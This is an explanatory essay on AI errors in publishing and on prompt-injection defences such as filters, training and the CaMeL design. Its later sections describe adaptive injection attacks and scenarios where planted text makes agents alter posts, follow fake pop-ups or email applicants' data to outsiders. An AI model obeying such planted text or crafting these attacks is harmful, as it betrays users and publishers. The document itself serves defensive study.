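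King Features already had a "strict policy" against using AI to create content, according to a company statement reproduced in Fox 32 Chicago's *Chicago Sun-Times issues response after publication of fake book list*. The company stopped working with Buscaglia, who it said had not disclosed his use of AI. A ban that relies on writers to report their own AI use doesn't catch those who hide it, and it may have given editors a reason not to check.

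### Quotations that nobody said

The second case came out of the matplotlib dispute. On 13 February 2026, the technology news site Ars Technica published an article about the agent that had attacked Scott Shambaugh. The article attributed quotations to Shambaugh, who pointed out that he had never said them. The site took the article down, and two days later its editor-in-chief, Ken Fisher, confirmed in an *Editor’s Note* (2026) that an AI tool had generated the quotations.

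The article had two bylines. Futurism reports that the site later dismissed one of the writers, its senior AI reporter Benj Edwards. Evidently, even an experienced specialist at a publication that had covered this danger for years could make the mistake.

If Shambaugh is right that his blog's block on AI agents kept the tool out, the tool produced plausible quotations when it should have reported that it had no text. Anyone reading the draft would have seen quotations that looked like real ones. Searching Shambaugh's blog for each quotation would have exposed the problem, but no one at Ars Technica did this thoroughly enough.

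Ars Technica also had a written policy, which TheWrap's *Ars Technica Fires Reporter Over AI-Generated Quotes* describes as requiring clear labels on AI-generated material. Labeling the article would have complied with that policy but left the invented quotations in place.

### How often AI answers about news are wrong

Incidents like these don't show how often models get facts wrong, because nobody counts the accurate articles. *Evaluating Commercial AI Chatbots as News Intermediaries* (Suzgun, Shen and colleagues, 2026) is the most detailed recent measurement. For two weeks in February 2026, the team gave six chatbots with web search 2,100 questions, each with five possible answers, drawn from same-day BBC reports in six languages. They then made the task harder in two smaller tests.

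| Test | Wrong answers |
|---|---|
| Five options, best chatbot (Gemini 3 Flash) | 4% |
| Five options, average of six chatbots | 12% |
| No options, one day's questions | 29–30% |
| Question contains a false detail, best of four chatbots (Grok 4) | 30% |
| Question contains a false detail, worst of four (GPT-5) | 81% |

The test without options is closest to what a publishing application does, since the application isn't given five versions of a fact to choose from, but it covered only one day. Three models marked the answers. One of them, Gemini 3 Pro, was also among the chatbots tested, though all three agreed on 95 per cent of the answers.

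When a question contained a false detail, GPT-5 accepted it 64 per cent of the time. One question took a figure of 53 per cent that the BBC had reported from one organisation and attributed it to another. A chatbot that matched only the number would get the answer wrong. Writers make similar mistakes when they ask a tool for a quotation that a person never gave or for a new novel by an author who hasn't written one.

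The researchers wrote these questions to mislead the chatbots and asked each one only 100 of them, all in English, so the results don't describe ordinary use. The study also had no human comparison, and companies have since replaced several of the models. On the other hand, the BBC is easy to find on the web, so chatbots may do worse with a small-town newspaper. The chatbots made mistakes on 21 per cent of the Hindi questions, roughly twice the rate for any other language.

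Journalists who mark complete answers find more problems. In a 2025 test organised by the European Broadcasting Union (EBU), an association of public broadcasters, 22 broadcasters in 18 countries assessed ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity (EBU, *News Integrity in AI Assistants*, 2025). They marked about 3,000 answers, according to DW, and 20 per cent had major accuracy problems, such as invented details or outdated information (EBU, 2025).

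Gemini did worst in the broadcasters' test, with significant problems in 76 per cent of its answers, yet a Gemini model came first in the test by Suzgun and colleagues. The two tests used different generations of Gemini and marked answers differently. The broadcasters marked Gemini down mostly for poor sourcing, which didn't count towards accuracy in the other study. Broadcasters also have a stake in how AI companies use their work, and may be strict about credit. Sourcing still matters to publishers, because an editor can't check even a correct statement without knowing where it came from.

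NewsGuard's *Quarterly AI False Claim Monitor* (2026) reports that 11 chatbots repeated false claims more than 28 per cent of the time in January 2026. NewsGuard started with ten claims it knew to be false, so this isn't an error rate for news in general. In the 2025 audit described in Axios' *Popular chatbots amplify misinformation* (2025), it asked about each claim neutrally, then as if it were true, and then in a way designed to get around the chatbot's safeguards. That method is better suited to studying deliberate misuse than to estimating how often an honest reporter will get a wrong answer.

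The fact-checking charity Full Fact asked several chatbots the same 22 questions every day for ten weeks. *Wrong on Sunday, right on Monday* reports many accurate answers, but also outdated rules presented as current and rules from one part of the UK presented as if they applied everywhere. A council could easily publish either kind of mistake, because the text sounds official and was once true or is true elsewhere.

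### Restricting sources and checking claims

In the study by Suzgun and colleagues, 72 per cent of errors occurred because the chatbot failed to find a relevant source or used a different one with different details. Only 3 per cent occurred because it misread the right source. An application that gives the model the right document therefore avoids the most common cause of error. The town's assistant should write from the club's notice and the page the club linked to, and have no general web search.

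Restricting sources would have protected the council against a page like Germain's, but only because nobody at the gardening club is trying to deceive it. The publisher, rather than the model, has to decide whom to trust, which is easy for local events but much harder for a news site. Switching off web search raised the chatbots' error rates on same-day American news by 31 to 46 percentage points, and a short list of approved sites can leave out the one that has the story.

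A reputable source can also be the wrong one for the purpose. A BBC Hindi article reported that Indians make up 7 per cent of the world's merchant sailors, but chatbots answered with 10 to 12 per cent, which they had reported accurately from English-language maritime reports. The publisher therefore has to link each statement to a particular document rather than rely on a general list of good sources.

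Quotations are the easiest thing to check. Ordinary software can search the source for the exact words and block publication if they aren't there. It should also block publication if it can't open the source, which may have been the problem with Shambaugh's blog. A reporter would then have to open the page or ask him. This check would have stopped the Ars Technica article, but it can't detect a quotation that is out of context or attributed to the wrong person.

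Dates, prices and book titles are nearly as easy to check. The council's second program can compare the date in the draft with the date field on the form, and a publisher can look up each title in a library catalogue. Less precise claims need a reader who understands them, because a draft can match its source in every name and number and still call a proposed road closure "approved".

A second model can help with those. The three models that marked the free answers agreed closely, which is encouraging, but they had a correct answer to compare with. A model that has to find the correct answer itself has the same search problem that caused most of the errors, and it may also find the page that misled the first model. The checking model should get the draft and the same source document as the writer, and flag anything the document doesn't support.

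### Sign-off and corrections

Somebody presumably approved both the supplement and the Ars Technica article for publication, and each organisation had a rule about AI. But neither process guaranteed that the person approving the text had compared it with anything. Language models are very good at writing text that sounds right, so an editor who reads only the draft, and judges it by how it sounds, may miss invented facts.

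A better approval page would show the source next to the draft, with every date, price, name and quotation highlighted. The clerk could compare the plant sale's details with the notice in less than a minute. A newspaper that buys material could refuse any list or quotation that arrives without its sources. This adds work for the supplier, but much less than each customer would need to repeat the research.

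After a mistake, a publisher can delete the text or correct it publicly. The Philadelphia Inquirer removed "Heat Index" from its publishing system, which stopped further electronic copies but did not affect the printed ones. Ars Technica replaced its article with an editor's note, so anyone following an old link learned that the quotations were false, which seems clearly better than finding an empty page. The note also gives other people's AI systems a correction to find, although Full Fact's results suggest that some of them will keep repeating the old version.

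A correction doesn't reach most people who saw the mistake and never returned. The town could send one through the same channels as the original post, which for the plant sale were the website, the weekly email and the social media feed. This requires the application to record where each post went.

### Labels and the EU disclosure rule

Another proposal is to tell readers that a model wrote the text. The European Union has required this in some cases since 2 August 2026. Under Article 50(4) of the AI Act, as summarised by Paul, Weiss, organisations must disclose when they use AI to generate or alter text published to inform the public on matters of public interest.

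The organisation is exempt from disclosure if the text has gone through human review or editorial control and a person or company holds editorial responsibility for it. The European Commission (2026) explained this exemption in its guidelines of July 2026. According to the law firm Stephenson Harwood, a cursory check doesn't qualify, and a significant AI change after the review cancels the exemption. An editor who approves an article and then lets a model rewrite its opening therefore has to review it again or label it.

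The guidelines define public interest broadly, to include politics, public administration, health, consumer safety and cultural matters open to public debate. If the town were in the EU, an AI-written post about a change to council tax would need a proper review or a label, but a post about a plant sale probably wouldn't. CADE's *European Commission publishes guidance on AI Act transparency requirements* adds that routine spelling and grammar corrections are exempt and organisations can follow a voluntary code of practice to show that they comply.

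The exception is sensible, since it rewards publishers for checking and keeps somebody responsible. But it also means that an article without a label may be entirely AI-written. Its reviewer may also have missed an invented quotation.

Readers also can't learn much about accuracy from a label, which describes how the text was produced. An AI-written post with the correct date and price would carry the same label as one with both wrong. Germain could publish his hot-dog article without a label because he wrote it himself. The separate rule on machine-readable marks has the same limit. PPC Land reports that these marks are meant to record that content is artificial, not who made it.

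Records of origin are more useful inside a newsroom. If the publishing system stores which passages came from a model and which sources the model had, an editor knows what to check first. After an error, the editor can also find other articles made the same way. Ars Technica said it reviewed recent work after the retraction and found no further problems. Such records would make that kind of review quicker and more reliable.

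A line such as "Date and price checked against the organiser's notice on 3 April" would help the town's readers more than "Written with AI", though the council could print both. The application should add the first line only after the clerk has checked those details against the notice, because a model could write it even if nobody had.

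## Filters and trained models tested against adaptive attackers

Splitting an application into two programs, or removing a tool, limits the damage after a model follows planted text. Other defences try to stop the model from following it. They are popular because a developer can add one without redesigning the application, and many scored very well in their inventors' own tests.

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues attacked twelve of these defences and bypassed most of them in more than 90 per cent of test cases. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, whose products depend partly on such defences.

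### Marking, training and filtering

The easiest defence to add is to mark the untrusted text. In spotlighting, the application puts special markers between its own instructions and outside text, and tells the model what the markers mean. Microsoft uses this method, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*. The town's assistant would receive the gardening club's page inside the markers, with an instruction to treat it only as material for the post. Prompt sandwiching repeats the task after the outside text, so that the council's instructions are the last thing the model reads. Both methods depend on the model following the council's instructions over any in the outside text.

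Developers try to train models to follow an instruction hierarchy more reliably. In this hierarchy, the operator's system prompt outranks the user's request, and both outrank anything in a web page or a tool's result. Google DeepMind (2025) describes one method, in which an automated attacker plants injections in realistic tasks and developers train Gemini to ignore them and complete the user's request. SecurityWeek reports that in an email test, one adaptive attack succeeded 99.8 per cent of the time against Gemini 2.0 and 53.6 per cent of the time against the trained Gemini 2.5.

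A filter, or classifier, is a separate and usually smaller model that judges whether a text contains an attack. It can screen the main model's input or output. Most filters learn from known attacks and harmless text, and they usually judge a text without knowing the task. This seriously limits them, because a request that is routine in an email from the mayor's office can be an attack when it appears in a resident's notice.

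Companies usually combine these methods. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* lists filters, a trained model, removal of suspicious URLs and requests for user confirmation.

### Twelve defences, before and after adaptation

A fixed attack is a text written in advance and used unchanged against every defence. An adaptive attacker watches how the defended system responds, rewrites the text and tries again. Nasr and colleagues argue that developers had mostly tested their defences against fixed attacks, or against general-purpose attack programs not tailored to the defence being tested.

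The paper's own attacks all used the same loop: propose candidate texts, score them, and use the best to write the next batch. In the search version, a language model rewrote the texts and could query the defended system up to 800 times per scenario. A second version used reinforcement learning, which trains the attacking model on its own successes. A third used calculations on the target model's internal numbers, and in the fourth, people wrote the attacks.

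| Defence | How it works | Fixed attack succeeds | Adaptive attack succeeds |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 30% | 100% |
| Spotlighting | Marks off outside text | 28% | 99% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the task after outside text | 21% | 95% |
| RPO | Adds an optimised safety prompt | | 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model on attacks | | 100% |
| StruQ | Trains the model to separate instructions from data | | 100% |
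| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to ignore injections | 5% | 96% |
| Protect AI Detector | Filter | 15% | 90% |
| PromptGuard | Filter | 26% | 94% |
| PIGuard | Filter | 0% | 71% |
| Model Armor | Google's filter | 28% | 90% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether outside text disrupts a secret test task | | Every case |
| MELON | Runs the model twice and compares its tool calls | 0% | 89% |

The rows with two figures come from the AgentDojo test suite, run with Gemini 2.5 Pro except for MetaSecAlign, which is itself a model. The other four defences went through different tests. RPO and Circuit Breakers mainly address jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get forbidden content out of a model, so their results are weak evidence about planted text.

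The usual summary of this study, that defences went from nearly perfect to useless, fits PIGuard, MELON and MetaSecAlign, but not spotlighting and two of the filters when used with Gemini. Those three hardly reduced the success rate of even the fixed attack, so they had little protection to lose.

The successful texts rarely looked like attacks. Many presented the attacker's action as a necessary step in the user's task, or as routine office policy. A filter can't block such wording without also blocking legitimate text. PIGuard resisted attacks best of the four filters, but it reduced the share of ordinary tasks that Gemini completed from 74 per cent to 39 per cent, which would be too large a loss for a council publishing event notices.

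MELON runs the model a second time, in secret, to reveal planted instructions. On Llama 3.3, the attacking model's search beat this defence in 76 per cent of cases without knowing about the second run, and in 95 per cent once it had a description of the defence. The attacking model wrote instructions that applied in only one of the two runs.

Nasr and colleagues conclude that prompting defences don't make a model more robust. Their result for spotlighting on GPT-5 Mini doesn't quite fit, because the search succeeded in 47 per cent of cases, compared with 75 per cent without a defence. But this difference may be due to chance, since the search varied a lot from run to run and the team ran it only once per scenario.

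Later work found similar but smaller effects. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment*, a paper from June 2026, tested several defences of a small open model. On average, the most successful fixed attack on each defence worked 21.7 per cent of the time, and the most successful adaptive attack worked 41.8 per cent of the time. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) tested spotlighting against attacks that tamper with the user's task instead of telling the model to drop it. Spotlighting lowered the attacks' success rate from 11.1 to 8.1 per cent for Claude Sonnet 4.5 but left it at about 17 per cent for Kimi K2.5.

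### The human attackers

For the human part of the study, Nasr and colleagues ran an online competition with more than 500 entrants and $20,000 in prizes. Entrants wrote a text, watched the agent's reasoning and tool calls as it read the text, and tried again. They didn't know which defence, if any, they faced, but at least one entrant beat each challenge.

People and the automated search both attempted 29 of the scenarios. Between them, the people succeeded in all 29, while the search succeeded in 69 per cent. This comparison favours the people because it sets the combined results of many entrants against a single run of the search. Only three entrants attempted all 29 scenarios. The best of them succeeded in 75 per cent, and the other two did worse than the search.

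Most individual submissions failed, but a low success rate per submission does not show that a defence is secure. In one challenge, the attackers won even though only 0.2 per cent of the submissions against GPT-5 Mini got through, with or without prompt sandwiching.

### Results for newer models

Models have improved since then, at least against attacks not tailored to them. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that in Anthropic's tests, injections failed against Claude Opus 5 in all 129 browser scenarios. In a broader test by the security company Gray Swan, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 2.0 per cent of the time against Opus 5 and 5.5 per cent of the time against Opus 4.8. Anthropic has since released newer models, including Mythos 5.2, which Mowshowitz (2026) reviewed in November in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*.

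No successes in 129 scenarios is a very good result, but it doesn't show that the true rate is zero. If the scenarios were a random sample, the true rate could still be as high as about 2.3 per cent.

According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026), GPT-5.6 rarely failed in OpenAI's tests when the attack came through the chat, but failed more often when it came through tools and outside content.

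Independent researchers who let the attacker adapt measured much higher attack success rates. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested seven browser agents on 1,024 tasks, with up to 64 attempts per task. The original injections succeeded on 0.5 to 4 per cent of tasks. After the attacker adapted them, they succeeded on 31 per cent of tasks against Claude Sonnet 5, 65 per cent against GPT-5.5, and 79 to 95 per cent against the other five.

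That test also separated attacks that only change the agent's answer from attacks that change something in an application. Sonnet 5 gave the attacker's answer in 41 per cent of cases, but made the attacker's change in only 8 per cent. For GPT-5.5 the figures were 81 and 29 per cent. Publishers publish the answer, so an outsider may need only the easier attack.

In the most demanding recent test, Google DeepMind researchers set 16 cooperating AI agents to attack a model in 100 invented scenarios (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026, *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*). The agents shared notes and had a combined 320 attempts per scenario. In one scenario, a user wants to book a tutoring session, and the planted text has to make the model record some health readings as well.

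The goals were deliberately harmless. A model may refuse to delete files because the action is harmful, without detecting that the instruction came from an untrusted source. Harmless goals test whether the model follows instructions only from trusted sources. This test is relevant to publishing, where a planted request to change "Saturday" to "Sunday" looks harmless.

Gemini 4 Argon, the most resistant model in the test, followed the planted instruction in 13 scenarios within 150 attempts and in 34 by the end. Google's older Gemini 3.6 Flash and the open models Kimi K3, GLM-5.3 and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash each followed it in 99. The researchers had switched off the filters that Google normally runs outside its models, so the finished product should be more resistant.

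### Why the figures don't compare

| Test | Model | Attempts allowed | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan | Claude Opus 5 | 15 | 2% |
| *BrowseSafe++* | Claude Sonnet 5 | 64 | 31% |
| *BrowseSafe++* | GPT-5.5 | 64 | 65% |
| Kurakin and colleagues | Gemini 4 Argon | 150 | 13% |
| Kurakin and colleagues | Gemini 4 Argon | 320 | 34% |

The attackers in this table had different numbers of attempts, different goals and different levels of skill, so the results do not show that Opus 5 is seventeen times safer than Gemini 4 Argon. The attacker's skill matters a great deal. When Kurakin and colleagues used Gemini 3.8 Flash as the attacker, Gemini 4 Argon resisted in every scenario for 150 attempts. The 13 per cent figure came from changing only the attacker, to a second copy of Gemini 4 Argon.

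The success rate of an attack also depends on the setting. VentureBeat reports that one attack on Claude Opus 4.6 failed in all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, but that a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time when the model operated a graphical interface.

The scoring method can change the measured success rate of attacks by several percentage points. *INFUSE* (2026) reported an average success rate of 19.6 per cent when a language model judged its attacks and 15.4 per cent when fixed rules did.

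Results are safer to compare within one test than across tests. *BrowseSafe++* gives a fair reason to prefer Sonnet 5 to GPT-5.5 for reading untrusted pages, at least until newer versions of both go through the same test.

### The arithmetic of repetition

Anthropic tested its browser extension against an attacker that combined many techniques known to work. PYMNTS reports the attacker's success rate as 1 per cent and describes it as a meaningful risk. An attacker can usually try again, so the chance of at least one success can be higher than 1 per cent.

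If each attempt has a 1 per cent chance of success, a hundred attempts all fail with probability 0.99^100, or about 0.37, so the chance that at least one succeeds is about 63 per cent. For n attempts with success rate p, the chance of at least one success is 1 − (1 − p)^n.

| Success rate per attempt | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts | 10,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 63% | Over 99.9% | Over 99.9% |
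| 0.1% | 10% | 63% | Over 99.9% |
| 0.01% | 1% | 10% | 63% |

If a defence cuts the attack success rate tenfold, the publisher can face about ten times as many attacks at the same risk. To keep the chance of any success below 1 per cent over 1,000 attacks, the success rate would need to be below about 1 in 100,000. None of the tests above is large enough to show a rate that low.

Suppose a site processes 5,000 comments a day, one comment in a thousand contains an attack, and each attack has a 1 per cent chance of succeeding. In this case n is the number of attacks, not the number of comments. The site faces five attacks a day, or 150 in a month, so the chance that at least one succeeds during the month is about 78 per cent.

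Nobody knows the true share, and it could be far lower. Khodayari and colleagues found planted instructions on about eight web pages in a million. At that rate, 5,000 texts a day would contain one attack every 25 days, and the first success would take about seven years on average. But those were ordinary web pages, where few people were targeting a particular reader. An attacker trying to take over one site's assistant can post a hundred comments in an afternoon.

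A high volume of comments also makes filters harder to use. If a filter wrongly flags 1 per cent of honest comments, the site's moderator gets about 50 false alarms a day alongside at most five real attacks.

### What independence leaves out

The formula assumes that every attempt has the same chance of success and that attempts are independent. Real attacks violate these assumptions in ways that can make the formula's result too high or too low.

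If the model detects the trick in a comment once, it will probably detect it again, so posting the same comment a hundred times does not give an attacker a hundred independent chances. An average success rate of 1 per cent might even mean that one type of attack in a hundred always works and the rest never do, in which case repeating a randomly chosen one achieves almost nothing.

The Opus 4.6 figures show this effect. If each attempt had an independent 17.8 per cent chance of success, the chance of at least one success would have reached 79 per cent by the eighth attempt. VentureBeat reports 78.6 per cent, but only by the 200th attempt (57.1 per cent with Anthropic's extra safeguards switched on). Presumably some cases were easy and others close to impossible.

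Attackers who learn from failure have the opposite effect, since their later attempts are better than their first. In the test by Kurakin and colleagues, attackers had succeeded against Gemini 4 Argon in 13 scenarios after 150 attempts. If the chance of success per attempt had stayed constant, they would have succeeded in about 26 after 320 attempts, but they succeeded in 34. With only 100 scenarios, that difference could be chance, but it is what one would expect from agents that share notes.

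The formula is therefore a poor forecast for any particular site, but it is still a useful reminder that blocking 99 per cent of attacks does not necessarily make a site safe.

### Who can afford to get through

These results can be read as showing that the defences fail, because a determined attacker gets through, or that they help, because they make attacks harder and stop unskilled people. The first reading is the better basis for planning when an application controls something valuable.

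*SecPO* (2026) presents a training method that cut the success rate of attacks on an open model, Qwen3.6-27B, about tenfold. The method also raised the average cost of a successful attack from $5.92 to $34.90. The real increase is larger, since an attacker also pays for failed attacks. But even several hundred dollars is very little to somebody who hopes to take $150,000 from a wallet like Grok's.

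On the town's events page, the same increase might be enough. Few people would spend $35 and an evening's work to change the listed day of a plant sale to Sunday. Many more would paste in a trick they had seen online, and a trained model or a filter will stop most of those attempts. Stopping them would be enough to produce OWASP's "defense effect" in the incident records, even though it would not protect anyone from a skilled attacker.

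The benefit may not last, because attackers can use better models too. People who don't know how to write injections can have an agent write them. Kurakin and colleagues ran their attacking Gemini models without the usual safety filters, so the public versions may refuse to write injections, but the open models they tested could also attack weaker targets. For example, Gemini 3.6 Flash withstood all 150 attempts by Kimi K3 in only about 9 per cent of scenarios.

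An attacker who can guess which model the council uses can rent access to it, test hundreds of texts in private and submit only the best one, so the council's server would record a single notice. Limits on submissions still help against people who practise on the live site, as does not explaining why a notice was rejected. In the study by Nasr and colleagues, the attacking program received the filter's confidence score after each attempt, which a real application has no reason to reveal.

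The council should therefore use these defences where they have little downside. It should choose a model with a good record of handling strangers' text safely, even if a cheaper one writes equally good posts, because Gemini 4 Argon and Gemini 3.6 Flash differed greatly on this. It should also use a filter to send suspicious notices to the clerk rather than delete them, so that a false alarm takes the clerk a minute to check and the gardening club doesn't lose its notice.

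A correct post doesn't mean that nothing went wrong. *SecPO* examined one set of 140 successful attacks, and in 75 of them the model also completed the user's real task. The plant sale could appear with the right date, price and opening hours while the clerk's assistant did something else in another part of the site. A record of the assistant's tool calls would reveal the other action, and withholding the permissions it requires would prevent it.

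Nasr and colleagues left out designs such as CaMeL, which assume that the model will be fooled, because their attacks were bound to fail in most of the scenarios. Some early evidence suggests that adaptation helps less against controls outside the model. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) tried one hand-written adaptive attack on such a control, Progent. The attack succeeded 2.6 per cent of the time, compared with 4.2 per cent for the standard attack.

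## CaMeL: limiting what injected text can do

Filters and model training are meant to stop a model from obeying planted text. CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind, is based on the assumption that planted text will sometimes succeed, so it limits what the application can do afterwards. Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues described it in 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*.

CaMeL divides an agent's work between two models and an interpreter, which is an ordinary program. The first model, the planner, sees the user's request but none of the outside text, and writes a plan as a short computer program. The second, the quarantined model, reads the outside text and extracts what the plan needs, but has no tools. The interpreter runs the plan, records where each value came from, and checks a policy before every tool call.

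Willison introduced the two-model split in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023) and later explained a flaw in his version in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. An attacker who can edit the notes can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead. The planner then sends the document there, even though it never read the planted text. CaMeL adds the tracking and the policies to prevent this.

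### From today's notices to draft posts

Suppose the town council's clerk types "turn today's notices into draft posts". The planner knows this request and has descriptions of the tools, but it hasn't seen the notices. In simplified form, it might write this plan:

```python
for notice in get_notices("today"):
    post = ask_quarantined_model(
        "Extract the page, title, date, place and description",
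        notice)
    save_draft(post.page, post.title, post.date,
               post.place, post.description)
```

The last of three new notices announces a chess evening, but its description also contains instructions to delete the swimming-pool page and to put the post on the "Pay a bill" page. Suppose the quarantined model follows both.

The swimming-pool page is safe because the plan contains no call that deletes anything. The quarantined model can write "delete the page" into one of the five fields, but there it is only text. The other order gets further, since the plan does let the quarantined model say which page a notice belongs on. The interpreter now holds these values:

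| Value | Content | Source | Policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| `page` | "pay-a-bill" | Chess notice, through the quarantined model | Refuse |
| `title` | "Chess evening" | Same | Allow |
| `date` | 17 April | Same | Allow |
| `place` | "Library" | Same | Allow |
| `description` | "Beginners welcome" | Same | Allow |

A CaMeL policy is a Python function. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain, it receives the tool call, its arguments and their labels, and it returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. The council's policy could be very short:

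```python
def check_save_draft(page, title, date, place, description):
    if came_from_notice(page) and page.value != "events":
        return deny("A notice cannot choose this page")
    return allow()
```

The interpreter therefore refuses to save the chess notice as a draft of the "Pay a bill" page. The same policy would have allowed the save if the clerk had named that page in the request, because the page name would then have come from the clerk.

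The plan saves one draft for each notice, so a sentence such as "put this notice at the top of every page" has no effect. An honest request, such as "please mention that dogs are welcome", can still go into the description. Nobody has to work out which sentences in the notice are instructions.

CaMeL's labels also record who may read a value. The unpublished draft about the cancelled fireworks could carry a label that limits it to council staff, and a policy could keep anything derived from it out of public posts. The interpreter would then refuse a new post even if the quarantined model had used the draft only as a sample of house style, because it tracks which inputs the model received but not what the model took from them.

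### False dates and abuse in permitted fields

Suppose somebody submits a notice in the gardening club's name with the wrong day for the plant sale. The plan runs normally and the policy allows the call, because dates are supposed to come from notices. A false date gets the same label as a true one from the same form. An insult in the description gets through for the same reason.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) illustrates the same limit with an assistant that emails today's schedule to the user's boss. Text planted in the calendar can't add a step or change the recipient, but it can rewrite the message. This is a leftover risk for an email assistant, but it is most of the risk for a publisher, because the public reads the text the model writes.

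Narrow fields are a better option than forbidding all text from notices in posts, which would leave the council with nothing to post. A field that accepts only a date can't carry an insult or a link, and ordinary code can copy the date from the form without a model. This doesn't work for the description, which has to be free text to be useful.

How much an injected notice can alter also depends on the plan. The plan above gives the quarantined model one notice at a time, so the chess notice can spoil only its own post. If the clerk asked for a weekly round-up, the planner might put all the notices into a single call, and the chess notice could then change the date given for the plant sale.

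Debenedetti and colleagues ran into this limit in their own tests of CaMeL, where two attacks succeeded, according to *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026). In one, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a document said, and the attacker had changed the document. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, including the attacker's, and the benchmark counted this as a successful attack. Travel sites that quote their customers do the same thing intentionally. Garby and colleagues note that four independent systems fail on cases of this kind, and they see this as a limit of the whole approach rather than a weakness of any one design.

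Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, object that CaMeL doesn't inspect the agent's final answers. A document summary could repeat a planted line telling the reader to forward a file. They propose checking each answer for suspicious links and instructions, partly with another model. That would catch crude cases, but attackers can adapt to the checking model as they can to other filters. Checking the draft against the original notice would help the council more.

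### The exact guarantee

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, define the guarantee precisely. It has two parts:

- The agent can make only the tool calls that its plan provides for, and only the user's request and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions, determine the plan. This is called control-flow integrity.
- Every tool call has to satisfy the security policies.

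The guarantee does not cover whether a value is true. It holds only if the request is trustworthy, the policies match what the council intended, and the interpreter tracks values correctly. A clerk who pastes a resident's email into the request exposes the planner to untrusted text.

Planted text can also affect which of the plan's existing paths the agent follows. If the plan sends complaints to a colleague and events to the website, a complaint disguised as an event can end up on the website. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues call this branch steering in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. The agents' plans included a step for closing cookie pop-ups, so the researchers put a fake pop-up in an advertisement, which could lead the agent to an attacker's website.

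Some requests undo the separation altogether. Garby and colleagues switched off CaMeL's policies and told it to read a file and follow the file's instructions precisely. The planner wrote a program with a branch for every tool, and the text of the file determined which branch ran. Two attacks succeeded this way. A clerk who told the assistant to "do whatever the notices ask" might get a similar plan.

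Garby and colleagues also found gaps in the tracking. Suppose a plan has a line that changes a public variable only when a private condition is false. If the condition is true, the line doesn't run and the variable keeps its public label, but its unchanged value reveals that the condition was true. CaMeL can miss this because it updates labels only for lines that run. Peters-Gill and colleagues accept the criticism and say that their own extension of CaMeL has the same gap. This is a minor problem for an events page, since nearly everything it handles is meant for publication.

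The guarantee can also fail when agents pass work to each other. Suppose the council adds a newsletter agent with its own copy of CaMeL, and the events agent sends it the message "Add this to Friday's newsletter", followed by the description. The newsletter agent treats the whole message as its user's request, so its planner reads the planted text as a trusted instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated this with three agents handling job applications. An instruction hidden in a database made the last agent email the applicants' details to an outside address, even though each agent ran CaMeL correctly. Their fix sends instructions and data through separate channels and keeps the labels attached.

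### Benchmark results

AgentDojo, the test suite that simulates an agent's tools, has 97 ordinary tasks in email, banking, messaging and travel. In the June 2025 version of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL completed 77 per cent of tasks, compared with 84 per cent for an undefended agent. Tallam and Miller quote 67 per cent, from an earlier version.

*Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median task. For eighty-word notices, the extra tokens cost very little. Willison says the quarantined model can be smaller and cheaper than the planner, and may even run on the user's own computer.

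Other researchers have found that CaMeL completes far fewer tasks. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but it completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. *Kairos* (2026) also reports a completion rate below 50%. Both papers present competing defences, so the researchers had less reason to optimise CaMeL's performance.

*MetaPermit* (2026), which presents another competing defence, gives a plausible explanation. In its tests, CaMeL often produced a valid plan that stopped before the task was finished. An unfinished task still counts as a security success if the attack also fails. The result also depended on how reliably the model could write a program that CaMeL accepts, and the tests used one model, MiniMax-M2.7, for every defence without tuning.

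The test by Peters-Gill and colleagues is harder to dismiss, because one of them, Ilia Shumailov, also worked on the original CaMeL. On a set of industrial maintenance tasks shared among several agents, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures happened because the planner had to choose its steps before seeing any data. Unlike an ordinary agent, CaMeL can't respond to an unexpected result by adding a step that its planner didn't anticipate.

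The loss therefore seems to shrink as models get better at planning, though it was still considerable for the best models tested. It can be much larger on less predictable work, such as operating a computer through its screen, where Foerster and colleagues' version of CaMeL kept at most 57 per cent of the performance of leading models.

In a separate test based on AgentDojo, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL reduced the average attack success rate from 12.9 to 0.2 per cent. With the data channel added, no attack succeeded. The attacks were fixed, and GPT-5.5 resisted all of them even without CaMeL. These limitations matter less than they would in a test of a filter, because even an adaptive attacker can't add a call to a finished plan.

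### What the policies cost

Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without any policies. Garby and colleagues tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks with policies on and off. With them on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 tasks, roughly half as many as with them off. No attacks succeeded with the policies on, compared with a few when they were off.

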